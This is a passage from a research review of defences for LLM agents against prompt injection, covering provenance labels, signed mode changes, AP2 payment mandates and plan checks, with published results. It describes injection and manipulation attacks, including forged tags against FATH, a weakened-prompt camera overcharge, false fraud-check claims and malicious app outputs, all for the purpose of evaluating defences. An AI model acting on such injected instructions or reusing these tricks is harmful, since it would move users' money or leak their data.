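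They present CaMeL and FIDES as defences of this kind, which is only partly fair. CaMeL's policies can inspect individual arguments, and FIDES can require a trusted recipient while allowing an untrusted message. But the policies that Costa and colleagues used on AgentDojo did not check arguments, so their utility figures reflect the coarser approach.

PACT, the system by Fan and colleagues, gives every tool-call argument one of six roles. A recipient, web address or account number is a target, and the text of a message is content. The other four roles are commands, credentials, selectors (which choose an object) and controls (which change a tool's behaviour). Each value has a set of origins and a trust level, which PACT combines with the same kind of join as other label systems. Before a call, PACT checks that each argument meets its role's minimum trust level and has no origin that the role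 forbids. In the firm's case, the new account number would fail as a target, but the assistant could still quote it in the body of a message.

With perfect labels, PACT made no mistakes on a set of diagnostic tasks. On AgentDojo, with the three strongest of five models, it blocked every attack and completed 38.1% to 46.4% of the tasks, 8 to 16 percentage points more than CaMeL at the same level of security. Removing the roles made utility collapse, while removing the labels carried over from earlier steps let attacks through. An application therefore needs to track both where a value came from and how it is meant to be used.

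The perfect labels are hard to obtain in practice. When Fan and colleagues generated labels automatically for 20 real tools, the role was correct 87.1% of the time and the origin 77.4%. PACT uses the more cautious label when the right one is uncertain, which makes unnecessary blocking more likely than a missed attack. Other attempts to infer origins have had similar trouble. In the privacy tests by Zhong and colleagues, the language-model screener identified exactly the right categories of private data for 70% of tool calls. The classifier did so for 57%, no better than assuming that every call uses all the private data in the context.

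*Ghost in the Agent* tests provenance tracking on 400 scenarios from 20 agent frameworks. Its offline auditor was much better than FIDES at detecting when data from a particular source had reached a sensitive action.

#### When correct arguments aren't enough

A call can be wrong even when all its arguments are trusted. An attacker might get the assistant to send a genuine payment twice, or plant harmful code in a file that the user did ask the agent to edit. *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) covers these cases by requiring separate authority for the protected fields of a call, for the exact effect of any payload that changes something when it runs, and for making the call at all. Permission for a call can be used only once, which stops the second payment.

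Context-to-Execution Integrity (CXI) also defines origin more strictly. A tool's name always comes from the application's trusted list, but if an email led the model to choose that tool, CXI treats the choice as untrusted. To prevent such influence, the software generates each protected field separately, from a prompt that excludes untrusted text. If a field needs a value from an untrusted document, such as the path of a file that failed a test, trusted code validates the value and endorses it for that field only.

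Santos-Grueiro ran 720 episodes on AgentDojo and 400 on code repositories, and recorded no unauthorised action in the runs that CXI protected. Of the 400 coding episodes, 231 completed the task safely. Of the other 169, 73 failed because the software couldn't parse the model's output, 61 because nothing authorised the proposed change, and 35 because the change ran but didn't do the job. The total of 199 tasks completed safely on AgentDojo combines six conditions, so it doesn't measure the utility of CXI alone.

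A smaller test compared CXI with simpler mechanisms on 20 attacks and 6 legitimate actions:

| Mechanism | Attacks stopped |
|---|---|
| Approximate version of argument-level provenance | 12 of 20 |
| Permissions for each field, with no record of past calls | 10 of 20 |
| Separate reading and writing plus a record of calls, with no field check | 8 of 20 |
| CXI | 20 of 20 |

Argument-level provenance and CXI both allowed all 6 legitimate actions. Santos-Grueiro chose these attacks to expose particular gaps, so 12 out of 20 shouldn't be taken as a rate for real applications. The result does show that argument labels miss some attacks even when the labels work correctly, including attacks that involve the timing or repetition of a call.

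This precision requires a lot of work from developers. The policies covered 24 tools and other endpoints with 149 fields, 85 of which needed protection. The first audit found 18 mistakes, half of them high-severity. Some payloads that could change a system's behaviour weren't marked as such, and some approval fields accepted ordinary language.

### Ownership instead of trust levels

*LLM Agent Capabilities Should Follow Task Intent and Context Source* (Zheng, Zhang and Mao, 2026) assigns each field of an action to one type of source. The user's request supplies the goal, destinations and approvals. Workflow instructions supply the procedure, tool descriptions supply the available functions, and the running environment supplies observed values such as file contents. The paper separates sources by type because a single scale from untrusted to trusted can't express every rule. For example, a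 company's workflow instructions are more trustworthy than a random PDF, but they shouldn't decide where the user's money goes.

In their example, a user asks an agent to extract tables from two PDFs and report the results in a named code repository. Hidden text in a PDF names a different repository. The PDF belongs to the running environment, which doesn't own the destination field, so the checker looks for the repository's name in the user's request and rejects the call if it isn't there. The same rule catches accidental errors, such as the agent reading a table heading as the repository's name.

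Zheng and colleagues built this into a system called IntentCap. A language model proposes a short-lived permission for each action, and a deterministic checker accepts it only if every field comes from its owner. They replayed 3,746 security-sensitive events from four benchmarks, and IntentCap accepted no unsafe ones. It also covered all 3,813 legitimate actions in a separate test.

Their ablation tests how much it matters to keep the sources apart. When they merged all four into one trusted context, the checker wrongly accepted 3,593 of the 3,823 events that it should have rejected, or 94%. Merging only the environment with the tool descriptions produced 1,662 wrong acceptances. These were recorded events, though, with no live agent choosing its next step. Zheng and colleagues leave end-to-end attack success and attacks on the labelling to future work.

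Ownership works best when the user states the destination. If the user asks to pay the invoice on file, they have named a document but not an account number. The permission must then allow the number to come from that document, which again relies on the accounts being correct.

### What provenance adds to other checks

The *PACE* system by Li and colleagues combines provenance with an authority check, and their experiments separate the effects of the two. The provenance part graphs how data has moved between sources, tools and arguments. If a path leads from an untrusted source to a harmful effect, it looks for the smallest change that would break the path. The authority part derives the permitted actions and targets from the user's request, then checks the proposed call against them.

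They tested every combination on 1,167 cases with Qwen-3.8-27B. The table includes results from PASB, another benchmark for agent security:

| Checks switched on | AgentDojo attacks | AgentDojo tasks | AgentDyn attacks | AgentDyn tasks | PASB attacks |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Neither | 37.4% | 76.8% | 25.0% | 66.7% | 41.4% |
| Provenance | 0.0% | 13.6% | 0.0% | 0.0% | 31.0% |
| Authority | 0.0% | 64.6% | 1.7% | 36.7% | 0.0% |
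| Both | 0.0% | 65.2% | 1.7% | 36.7% | 0.0% |

On AgentDojo, provenance tracking alone stopped every attack but also most of the legitimate work. Nearly everything an agent does after reading a document depends on that document in some way, so the graph almost always contains a dangerous path. On AgentDyn, provenance tracking proposed breaking a path in 5,842 of 6,647 checked calls, and it could do so only by blocking the call, never by changing an argument.

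The authority check achieved the same security on AgentDojo with far more utility, and adding provenance to it made little difference. This is the strongest evidence against provenance as a separate requirement, but Li and colleagues did not separately test requests that don't specify the account number, where the number's origin may be the only clue that it is wrong.

The most effective attacks on AgentDojo succeeded against the complete system in 0%, 5.1% and 8.1% of cases across three models, compared with 48% to 100% for the undefended agents. Utility fell by less than 3 points. However, the tested version lets the authority check restore calls that the provenance check has blocked. The guarantee that no dangerous path remains applies to a stricter version, which Li and colleagues did not evaluate.

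#### Labels as a reason to ask a person

Aljumaily and colleagues suggest a more modest use of provenance, to decide when a person should take a second look. They tested policies on two small open models, Qwen2.5-1.5B and Qwen2.5-7B, in an environment with 13 tasks and 12 tools. The strongest policy allowed only the calls that the user's task needed. The larger model proposed the attacker's call in 84% of attacks, but the policy let only 7.7% through, and the agent completed 99% of its ordinary tasks with or without the policy. All the attacks that got through came from one task, in which the agent had permission to write a report and the attacker had it write something false.

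A policy on tool calls can't catch a false report, but a label can show that the agent had read untrusted text before writing it. Aljumaily and colleagues tested this only in simulation, assuming that 95% of labels survive and that reviewers miss more as they get tired. In the worst case, where the model always obeys the attacker, sending actions with this label to a reviewer reduced the attack success rate from 23.1% to 8.7%. This required 0.57 reviews per ordinary task. When all the labels were lost, the average harm rose only to its level with the policy alone. With labels and reviewers but no policy, the attacker eventually got a severe action approved every time.

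These numbers depend on the simulation's assumptions, and the experiments with real models contradicted one of them. The simulation assumed that an attacker who keeps trying will wear down any defence based on prompts and detectors, but one combination of the two stopped every attack on the larger model. Those attacks were fixed in advance, so a more determined attacker might still have succeeded.

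### Messages between agents

Suppose the firm splits its assistant into a mail agent and a payments agent. The mail agent reads the attacker's message, then uses its own key to sign an instruction telling the payments agent to use the new account number. The signature is valid and nobody altered the instruction on the way, but the account number still came from the attacker.

Authentication therefore can't replace provenance tracking. RAND's *Requiring Strong Authentication, Signed Data Exchange, and Integrity Checks* recommends proving the identity of both sides of a connection, encrypting the traffic and verifying that messages arrive unchanged. Those measures stop an outsider from impersonating the mail agent, but they don't record which document the agent was reading when it wrote the message. The payments agent needs that record too, as a label that stays attached to the account number.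 The message must still be signed, because otherwise an attacker could forge one with a trusted label.

Few experiments have tested provenance labels. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) is the most direct. It introduces MultiAgentDojo, a version of AgentDojo that divides the tools among several agents, and compares three systems across five models: one without CaMeL, one in which each agent has its own CaMeL, and one designed for the whole group. The comparison matters because separate copies of CaMeL can lose the label when one agent passes a message to another. The receiving agent must then either distrust every message, which blocks useful work, or trust them all, which lets the attacker's data through. The code and benchmark are public, so other teams can repeat the comparison.

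*SafeFlow* (2026) keeps labels attached as work passes between agents. In its main example, a user asks the system to read an SSH configuration file and email a secret token from it to an outsider. One agent retrieves the file, another rewrites the text and a third prepares the email. The label stays attached throughout, and a final check blocks the email. But language models help assign the labels and reconstruct the context, so the results can vary between runs.

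IntentCap also limits delegation by giving a subtask narrower permission than the task that created it, so an agent can't gain authority by asking another agent for help. Zheng and colleagues tested this and four other types of boundary in 38 checks. IntentCap blocked all 21 violations and allowed all 17 legitimate actions, but the test was very small.

In *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow*, Shim, Karim and colleagues (2026) found that an outsider can get private records from an agent without injecting any instructions. In one attack, the outsider creates a shared document and invites the agent to fill in its section. The agent treats this as ordinary teamwork and never checks whether the data's owner has consented. In another, the outsider asks the agent to tidy a list of real and invented records, and the ones it refuses to delete reveal which are real. A third attack makes the request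 in one channel and collects the answer in another, so a check that follows only one conversation misses the connection.

FlowSeal labels each sensitive record with its owner, based on where the record came from. Software outside the agent then checks everything the agent writes or shares. The shared-document attack leaked 52.2% of the targeted items before FlowSeal was added and 0.5% after. Across eight attacks, leakage stayed between 0% and 3.3%. The agent completed 72.4% of its legitimate tasks, compared with 75.9% for the best prompt-based defence. On live Gmail and Notion accounts, the attack based on deletions leaked 34.7% of the items under an earlier defence and none under FlowSeal.

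FlowSeal still relies on a language model for one step, comparing the outgoing text with the protected records to catch paraphrases. That model doesn't receive the conversation, so the outsider can't send it arguments directly. Shim and colleagues also leave prompt injection out of their threat model, so their results don't show whether a label would stop an attacker's account number from passing through the mail agent to the payments agent.

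## Evidence on signed intent for mode changes

Signatures are better suited to checking who may change the rules than to checking whether data is trustworthy, because a signed message can still contain untrustworthy data. In the email to the firm, the attacker claims that approvals are off. Some models readily accepted claims like that in Schwarz's test of session-scoped rules.

### What the signature has to cover

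A mode is the set of actions the application may take without asking anyone. Changing the mode needs a signature only if the change adds an action to that set. For the firm's assistant, turning approvals off adds sending transfers, so it needs a signature. Turning approvals back on removes that action, so the firm could let anybody do it, and the worst an attacker could cause that way is delay.

A digital signature depends on a pair of keys. The manager's private key stays on the manager's phone and turns a statement into a signature. Anyone with the matching public key can then check that this private key signed exactly this statement. To turn approvals off for an afternoon, the manager might sign the following:

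```
signer:   manager
session:  8841
change:   approvals on -> approvals off
limits:   up to £500 per transfer, saved payees only
expires:  17:00 today
nonce:    c93f07
```

Before changing the setting, a small program outside the model checks that:

1. the signature matches the manager's public key, and the manager may order this change;
2. the session number and the old mode match the session that is running;
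3. the new mode and its limits are ones the program can enforce exactly as written;
4. the expiry time has not passed;
5. the nonce, a number that works only once, is one the program issued and has not yet accepted.

The attacker's email fails the first check. Most of the other checks guard against replay, in which an attacker copies a genuine signed statement and submits it again. The session number stops an attacker from moving an unused statement to another session, and the nonce stops them from using a statement twice in the right session. *Zero-Trust Runtime Verification for Agentic Payment Protocols* (2026) likewise found that binding a payment approval to its context and allowing it only one use address different failures, and that a secure system needs both. The program also has to check and record the nonce in a single step, or two copies that arrive together could both pass.

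Signing mode changes is useless if the assistant can use the manager's key or edit its own settings file, as in the GitHub Copilot flaw that Dongol modelled.

### Signatures that the model has to recognise

*Signed-Prompt* (Suo, 2024) left part of the check to the model. An encoder built on GPT-4 replaced the sensitive word "delete" in the user's request with a secret word, "toeowx". A second model then had to write the real deletion command when it saw "toeowx" and an invalid command when it saw "delete", so an emailed order to delete everything would only cause an error. Despite its name, Signed-Prompt involves no cryptography, and the secret word works like a password.

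Suo tested signed commands with GPT-4 and a fine-tuned version of ChatGLM-6B, a small open model. The commands were direct, in several languages, reworded or only implied. No attacker's command succeeded on either model. GPT-4 carried out all the signed commands from users, while ChatGLM carried out 73% to 100%, depending on the type of command.

Suo doesn't give the number of test cases, but percentages such as 86.67% and 73.34% suggest groups of 15 or 30. If a group had 30 attacks and none succeeded, the true success rate could still be as high as 11.4% by the Wilson formula. The attacks were also weak, because they were ordinary commands without the secret word and none tried to make the model reveal it. Suo accepts that the defence works only while the word stays secret. Since the word doesn't change between requests, an attacker who learned it once could keep using it.

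*FATH* (Wang, Wu and colleagues, 2024) avoids a fixed password by generating five new tags for every query with HMAC, a standard method for computing a code from a message and a secret key. Two tags mark the user's instruction and the outside text. The other three divide the model's reply into its reasoning, its answer to the user and its answer to anyone else. The model may respond to an injected instruction, but it is supposed to put that response in the last section. Ordinary code then extracts the answer to the user and discards the rest.

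They used 100 texts for each of three injection tasks. Standard attacks succeeded in at most 2% of cases on GPT-3.5 and 10% on Llama 3 8B. The team then wrote attacks against FATH itself, which included made-up tags and told the model to put the attacker's answer in the authorised section. These are the attack success rates:

| Model and defence | Repeat a web address | Answer another question | Do a classification task |
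|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-3.5, no defence | 61% | 70% | 84% |
| GPT-3.5, FATH | 0% | 0% | 0% |
| GPT-3.5, FATH without the secret tags | 6% | 7% | 18% |
| GPT-3.5, FATH without the written policy | 34% | 38% | 56% |
| Llama 3 8B, no defence | 60% | 98% | 72% |
| Llama 3 8B, FATH | 26% | 34% | 31% |

FATH also stopped every attack in 510 simulated tool-use cases from another benchmark, InjecAgent, on both models. But average answer quality, on a ten-point scale, fell from 7.9 to 6.9 for GPT-3.5 and from 8.3 to 6.7 for Llama.

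The Llama results show why a secret in the model's context is weak protection. The attacker didn't need to know the tag, because the model had it in context and could be prompted to use it. In about three in ten cases, Llama put the attacker's answer in the authorised section, and the code passed it on because the tag was correct. On GPT-3.5, removing the written policy weakened the protection more than removing the secret tags. Much of the protection therefore depended on the model following the developer's instructions, which injections are designed to override.

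### Signatures that code verifies

If code checks the signature, the model doesn't need to hold any secret. *Identifying and Mitigating Vulnerabilities in LLM-Integrated Applications* (Jiang, Xu and colleagues, 2023) presents an early system of this kind, called Shield. The paper mainly addresses the threat of a dishonest app between the user and the model, such as a shopping assistant that secretly promotes one product. The user signs each query together with a session number, and a program in front of the model verifies the signature, so the app can't change the user's words without invalidating the signature.

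The app still has to add material, such as product details, and the signature can't show whether those additions are honest. Shield has the language model compare the app's prompt with the signed query. This detected 99% to 100% of attacks that introduced bias or toxic content when the model was GPT-4, and 71% to 100% when it was GPT-3.5. Jiang and colleagues ran actual attacks, but these rates measure the model's judgement rather than the signature. The attacks also targeted the text of answers, not tool calls or permissions.

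#### Authenticated prompts

Rajagopalan and Rao (2026), in *Protecting Context and Prompts*, sign the prompts that an agent generates as it works. For example, a request to analyse sales data might lead the agent to write a second prompt to search a particular report. The second prompt carries its own signature, the signature of the prompt it came from, the user's original request and a policy. The policy can only become stricter:

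allowed(new) = allowed(parent) ∩ allowed(tool) ∩ allowed(organisation)

denied(new) = denied(parent) ∪ denied(tool) ∪ denied(organisation)

Code at each tool verifies the signature and the policy before it runs the call, so nothing the agent derives from a request can have more permissions than the request had. In the firm's case, no prompt the agent wrote after reading the attacker's email could turn approvals off.

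The manager could turn them off only by starting a new request, whose policy comes from the user's role and the organisation's rules. That would be a natural place to require the manager's signature, but in this design the agent's own key signs the first prompt as well as the later ones. The signature shows that the agent's software issued the prompt, not that the manager approved it.

To prevent replay, each call includes a timestamp, an identifier for the context and a sequence number that rises with every step. The software also keeps a hash chain, in which each entry's fingerprint depends on the one before. If an attacker later inserts "User is admin" into the history, the fingerprints no longer match. But the chain records tool results as they arrive, so if the agent reads the same sentence in an email, it becomes a valid part of the history.

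Rajagopalan and Rao report 100% detection with no false positives across six attack categories. They describe one representative attack per category and don't give the number of trials, so this is mainly a design argument. The proof that permissions only shrink doesn't depend on those trials. They concede that the scheme doesn't verify intent or prevent an agent from misusing permissions it legitimately has.

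#### Intent certificates

In *Intent-Governed Tool Authorization for AI Agents*, Zhu and Wang (2026) propose certificates that a server derives from the user's message but the user does not sign. Each certificate lists the types of action the request calls for, the records and amounts involved, and an expiry time. A gateway hides any tool that the certificate doesn't cover and checks each call against it. The certificate can only narrow the permissions the application already has.

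The "admin" request type, which includes granting access, disabling features and changing policy, is the closest to a mode change. The design hides admin tools unless the user explicitly asks for such a change, and then requires a stronger review. However, the main set of 176 test tasks covers only reading, summarising, creating, updating, deleting and exporting.

Zhu and Wang also tested the whole system with three open models on synthetic tasks. In 198 trials with attacks or ambiguous requests, it carried out no unsafe action, but it accepted 40 unsafe drafts for a person to review. It didn't fully complete any of the 108 legitimate trials, though 36 produced a draft.

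The certificates may not be why these trials had no unsafe actions. Zhu and Wang didn't repeat the trials without certificates, and the gateway's older controls had already prevented every unsafe action on the 176 simpler tasks. In a separate test, the models identified the right type of action for 73% to 85% of requests, but the right limits on which records to use for only 18% to 58%. A mode change could avoid much of this difficulty because the manager can choose from a short list instead of describing a mode in free text.

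### Signed mandates for payments

Google's Agent Payments Protocol (AP2) uses signed authorisations, called mandates, for purchases by shopping agents. Google released the first version in 2025 and version 0.2 in April 2026. The checkout mandate shows the merchant what the user agreed to buy, and the payment mandate authorises the payment.

When the user is present, the merchant first signs the final basket. Both mandates contain a hash of that signed basket, so nobody can attach them to a different purchase. A "trusted surface", a display that doesn't use an LLM, shows the user the details and asks for consent before the signing.

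The user can also let the agent shop alone by authorising open mandates. According to AP2's documentation, these record the user's goals and constraints before there is a final basket. An open mandate names the agent's public key. The agent later signs the purchase with its own private key, and the merchant and payment companies check that the purchase meets the constraints.

An open mandate is in effect a signed mode change, because it switches the agent from asking about each purchase to buying on its own. It also divides the keys sensibly, since the agent can use its key to exercise the permissions it was given but not to gain new ones.

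#### Attacks that left the signatures valid

In *Beyond the Mandate*, Aviv, Gandh and colleagues (2026) independently analysed the security of version 0.2. They built their own deployment because no complete public one was available to test. They listed 48 threats, rated eight as high-risk and demonstrated all eight in five attacks, none of which involved forging a signature.

In one attack, a user asks the agent to buy a camera for no more than $50. A recent update has weakened the prompt of the sub-agent that compares mandates with the user's request, so the sub-agent now accepts differences that seem justified. The merchant claims in its catalogue that a $50 purchase may need authorisation for up to $80, and its quote tool returns a range of $50 to $80 without naming a payee. The agent therefore prepares a mandate with an $80 limit and no restriction on the payee. The trusted surface displays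 both as "checkout headroom", and the user approves. The merchant then charges $80, and every signature is valid.

Another attack is closer to the false claim about approvals, because an unsigned statement does switch off a safeguard. A fraudster with a stolen card runs their own shopping agent, which sends the payment companies unsigned data about fraud risk. In this data, the fraudster falsely claims that the cardholder has already passed an extra identity check, so the payment processor skips the check. Aviv and colleagues recommend accepting such data only if it is inside the signed mandate or comes with a signature from an authorised source.

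A third attack gets around the replay protection. The attacker advertises a merchant whose protocol address has the digit 1 in place of a letter l. An agent that doesn't compare addresses exactly will connect and fall back to version 0.1, which lacks the newer defences. The agent should refuse the connection instead.

These attacks show what can go wrong, but not how often. The testers ran them on a system they had built, and the camera attack also needed the weakened prompt. The general problem had already appeared in version 0.1. *Whispers of Wealth* (2026), on prompt injection against an AP2-style shopping agent, points out that mandates protect the execution of a purchase but not the reasoning behind it.

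None of the experiments on these designs specifically tests signed mode changes. The fraud example shows that an unsigned switch can be exploited, but not how well a signed one would resist attack. A direct test would run the same agent with and without the signature requirement while attackers tried to switch its mode. It would count how many unauthorised changes succeeded and how many legitimate ones failed.

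### Approval without understanding

The main objection to signed intent is that a signature proves only whose key signed a statement, not that the person understood it or that the agent's later actions match it. The camera buyer, for example, approved the $80 limit without realising that it let the merchant raise the price.

AP2 addresses the first problem with the trusted surface. Aviv and colleagues want this surface to also show the exact maximum, indicate when the payee is unrestricted, sign only what it displayed, and reject any limit higher than the one the user gave. The last rule would have stopped the camera attack even though the user was ready to approve, provided the software still had a reliable record of the original $50 limit.

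For the second problem, AP2 relies on the hash of the basket and on checks by the merchant and payment companies. Zhu and Wang split requests whose details aren't known yet. If a user asks an agent to find duplicate records and delete whichever one they approve, the first certificate allows only reading. Once the user has chosen a record, the server issues a second certificate for the deletion. Rajagopalan and Rao attach the original request to every later prompt so that another model can score how far the agent has drifted from it. They treat this score as advice and don't rely on it for security.

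Mandates can also serve as evidence in a dispute, according to AP2's *Agentic Payment Protocol (v0.2)*. Such evidence may help decide who bears a loss, but it doesn't prevent the loss, and it can be incomplete. In two of the attacks by Aviv and colleagues, the audit trail named only the payments platform, not the competitor that had misused it.

The objection is less serious for mode changes than for purchases. A firm has only a few modes, so it can write a fixed description of each one in advance, with no text from a merchant or a model. The manager's phone might display "Until 17:00, payments of up to £500 to saved payees will go out without your approval." The program can then enforce exactly those limits.

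An attacker could try to persuade the manager instead of the model, perhaps with an email complaining that approvals are holding up an urgent payment. If the manager signs, every transfer within the limits goes through without further review, including any caused by an injected instruction. The limits therefore matter as much as the signature. If they restrict payments to saved payees, for example, the program would still refuse a transfer to the attacker's new account number.

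## Experiments on checking plans before tool use

A signed limit of £500 per transfer caps the size of each transfer, but the firm's assistant still chooses what to do within that limit. A plan gate controls that choice by checking the intended sequence of actions before the first tool runs.

A check on a single tool call covers the tool's name and arguments, while a check on a whole plan also covers the order of the calls and how the result of one feeds into the next. If an assistant is allowed to read the accounts and email customers, each call is acceptable by itself, but a plan that reads the accounts and emails them to a customer is not. A plan check can also reject a job before any step runs. With call checks, an assistant replacing a standing order could cancel the old one and then be refused permission to create the new one.

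Checking each call has the advantage that the real values are available. A plan written in advance contains "pay the account on the invoice" rather than the account number, so a plan check has to work out where that number will come from.

Schwarz wants a check at the planning stage because the tested models often went from describing an action to carrying it out without being explicitly told to. In one scenario, which Schwarz did not test, planted text changes the planner's objective. Every later call may then look like a sensible step towards that objective, so a check on single calls has little evidence of the change.

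Researchers have tried three approaches: locking the plan before the agent reads anything untrusted, deriving a list of permitted actions from the user's request, and asking a second model whether an action fits the request.

### Fixing the plan first

CaMeL's planner writes its whole program from the user's request alone. *ACE* (Li, Mallick and colleagues, 2025) also hides the list of installed apps from its planner, because an attacker might have written one of them.

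They first showed why this matters by attacking IsolateGPT, which runs each app in its own environment. IsolateGPT's planner writes a detailed plan, but the system keeps only the list of apps, and a second model picks the next app after reading each result. In the example, a user compared fares from two taxi apps, QuickRide and MetroHail. QuickRide, the malicious app, returned an instruction instead of a price. The model then reported $54 for QuickRide and $85 for MetroHail, although MetroHail had quoted $54. In another attack, a line in QuickRide's description made the planner leave MetroHail out.

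ACE stands for Abstract-Concrete-Execute, and it handles a request as follows:

1. The abstract planner reads only the user's request. It invents the apps it would need, such as a document loader, and gives each a description and fixed types for its inputs and outputs. It then writes a program that uses them, in a restricted form of Python.
2. The concrete planner matches each invented app with an installed one. It judges every possible pair separately, so one app's description can't push another app out. If several matches work, it prefers the plan that needs fewer privileges.
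3. A static analysis, which examines the plan without running it, checks where data would flow.
4. The executor runs each app in its own container. A trusted program passes all messages between them and checks that every output has the right type.

In the taxi example, QuickRide's instruction isn't a number, so ACE shows MetroHail's real fare and an error for QuickRide.

The static analysis gives every app a clearance, written f, for the kinds of data it may receive. If an app's inputs have the labels x₁ to xₙ, the plan must satisfy:

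x₁ ⊔ … ⊔ xₙ ⊑ f

The app's output then gets the label f, since the app may have mixed in anything it was cleared to see. Loops need extra care, as in this plan:

```
a = ""
for i in range(4):
    network_send(a)
    a = load_bank_details()
```

The loop sends an empty string on its first pass and the bank details on its second. ACE analyzes the loop repeatedly until the labels stop changing, finds the leak and rejects the plan before anything runs.

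#### How well ACE works

Li and colleagues tested ACE on InjecAgent, a benchmark with 1,054 cases in which an app's output contains an injected instruction. ACE never called the attacker's app, whichever model did the planning. It called the right app without errors in 83.6% of cases with GPT-4o and 85.3% when o3-mini did the matching, but only about 60% with Claude 3.7 Sonnet or Qwen-2.5-72B. An earlier version also stopped every attack but called the right app without errors in only 47.2% of cases with GPT-4o. Better engineering raised this rate without affecting the security result.

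On a second benchmark, Agent Security Bench (ASB), ACE called an attacker's app 3 times in 2,000 trials. In all three, the app suited the user's request, so the injection wasn't the cause. By comparison, a version of Mistral-7B trained with StruQ followed 7% of the InjecAgent attacks.

These benchmarks only record which apps ran, but a third test, from the software company LangChain, checked whether the answers were correct. With GPT-4.1, ACE was correct on 95% of the tasks with a single tool, 80% of those with 26 tools and 85.7% of a set of database questions. The average request took 12 to 21 seconds and cost 1 to 27 cents. ACE took 12 seconds on the single-tool tasks, where IsolateGPT had taken 39.

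ACE's protection against false data is weaker. An attacker's account number has the same type as the supplier's, so the type check would accept it. The labels in the examples concern secrecy rather than trust. The analysis also depends on users labelling their data correctly. Li and colleagues chose Python because models write it well, but they can't prove that the analysis catches every leak in such a complex language.

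#### Plans that use yesterday's data

ACE handles one request at a time. *SPA* applies the same idea to agents that keep information between requests. For example, a user might ask an agent to fetch an invoice from Acme and keep the details on Monday, then ask it to pay the invoice on Tuesday. If an attacker has put a false account number in the invoice, the attack takes effect a day after the agent reads the invoice.

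SPA calls its planner once per request and gives it a description of each stored item but not the contents. The planner writes a complete plan from six kinds of step: retrieve a stored item, call a tool, have a quarantined model process some text, show something to the user, branch, and repeat. The planning language has no arithmetic or text templates, so a checker can determine exactly which values each step depends on.

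The checker gives each step a label that combines its inputs with pc, the label of the decisions that led to the step:

label(step) = pc ⊔ label(x₁) ⊔ … ⊔ label(xₙ)

Every tool has a minimum trust level for its inputs and a maximum secrecy level. If any tool call in the plan breaks either limit, SPA ends the whole request. It doesn't let the planner try again, because a planner that receives feedback could keep adjusting an unsafe plan until it passed. The Acme account number keeps its untrusted label overnight, so the checker would reject Tuesday's payment.

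The developers ran SPA on AgentDojo with gpt-5.4-nano, a small model, using 97 ordinary tasks and 949 attacks. They tried it with a planner that sees the installed tools and with one that invents its tools, as in ACE:

| Planner | Label checks | Tasks completed, no attack | Attack success rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| Sees the installed tools | Off | 53.0% | 0.4% |
| Sees the installed tools | On | 29.0% | 0.0% |
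| Invents its tools | Off | 14.1% | 0.0% |
| Invents its tools | On | 6.7% | 0.0% |

Fixing the plan before tool use provided nearly all of the protection. Without label checks, only four attacks succeeded, all on the same banking task. The checks stopped those four but rejected about 53% of all runs, usually because the plan passed a tool's untrusted output to a tool that required trusted input.

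The label checks are there to guard against false data, such as the Acme account number. AgentDojo hardly tests for this, so the checks' drawbacks seem to outweigh their benefits on these numbers alone.

The planner that invented its tools did badly because the software failed to match them with installed tools in about three-quarters of runs. In ACE's own test on InjecAgent, matching succeeded 84% of the time with GPT-4o. The weaker model used in the AgentDojo runs may explain some of the gap, but AgentDojo's tasks are also more realistic than InjecAgent's, so ACE's utility figures may be optimistic.

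The pattern was similar when each task was spread over two to five requests. With label checks, the attack success rate was 0.2% and the agent completed 35.3% of the tasks. Removing the checks raised these figures to 0.3% and 62.5%, and also letting the planner read the stored contents raised them only to 0.6% and 65.9%. The attacks weren't designed to stay in memory and take effect later, so these results don't show that reading stored text is safe.

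#### A plan found by ordinary search

*Capability Minimization as a Safety Primitive* (2026) describes a gate that finds a plan by ordinary search, so a language model doesn't have to write it. Each tool has a contract that lists what the tool needs, what it produces, its cost, its risk level and any authorisation it requires. The gate looks for the lowest-cost path from the current state to the goal, adding a penalty for any risky tool whose authorisation is missing. It then shows the agent only the first tool on that path. In the firm's case, the agent would not see the transfer tool until the manager's approval was on record.

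The agent can't call a tool that isn't available to it, so an injected order to use one fails. The contracts become the weak point, as the title of *The Gate Is Only as Honest as Its Contracts* (2026) suggests. Low-risk tools need no authorisation, so a transfer tool wrongly labelled low-risk would get past this check.

### Permissions derived from the request

The software often doesn't need a complete plan and can instead work out which actions a request could reasonably involve and block the rest. This limits each call but not the sequence of calls, so it only partly meets Schwarz's criterion. For example, an agent allowed to send one customer an email could send it ten times.

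*Contextual Agent Security* (Tsai and Bagdasarian, 2025) presents a system of this kind called Conseca. A language model reads the user's request, the tools' documentation and context that the developer has marked as trusted, then writes a policy. Ordinary code checks each action against the policy. In one example, Alice asks the agent to find unread work emails and reply to the urgent ones. The policy lets the agent send emails only from Alice, to addresses at work.com, with "urgent" in the subject line, and it forbids deleting anything. Each rule includes a short reason that a person can review and that the code returns to the agent if it blocks an action.

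The policy model never reads the emails themselves, so an instruction in one of them can't change the policy. But this protection depends on which context the developer chooses to trust. In the prototype, the trusted context includes email addresses and the names of all files and folders. Tsai and Bagdasarian acknowledge that an address could contain instructions, and the name of a saved attachment presumably could too.

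They tested Conseca on 20 file and email tasks with Gemini 1.5 Pro, averaging over five trials:

| Policy | Tasks completed | Blocked inappropriate actions |
|---|---|---|
| None | 14.0 of 20 | No |
| Fixed, allows everything except deletion | 12.2 of 20 | No |
| Fixed, allows no changes | 0.0 of 20 | Yes |
| Conseca | 12.0 of 20 | Yes |

The last column reports a test with a single planted email, which asked the agent to forward all messages about urgent security vulnerabilities to an employee. Conseca blocked the forwarding in every task except one, where the user had asked the agent to perform the tasks in urgent emails. The result is promising, but one email isn't enough to estimate an attack success rate.

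#### Progent and permissions that change during the task

*Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) lets the policy change as the agent learns more, whereas Conseca sets its policy once. Progent uses a solver to control the changes. Its policy is a list of rules about tool names and arguments. For example, a rule might let the agent send Slack messages only to a particular person. Progent blocks any call that no rule allows.

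In Progent, a language model writes the first policy from the user's request and may propose a new one after each tool result. An SMT solver, a program that decides whether logical conditions can hold together, then compares the new policy with the old one. Progent applies the new policy automatically if it allows only calls that the old one already allowed; otherwise, someone has to approve it. Shi and colleagues call this property monotonic confinement.

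In their main example, the user asks the agent to do whatever is in an email from Alice titled "TODOs for the week":

| What the agent has just read | Proposed change to the policy | Outcome |
|---|---|---|
| The user's request | Allow a search for that one email | First policy |
| Alice's list, which asks for a summary of recent emails on Slack | Also allow reading emails, looking up Slack details and posting on Slack | Needs approval |
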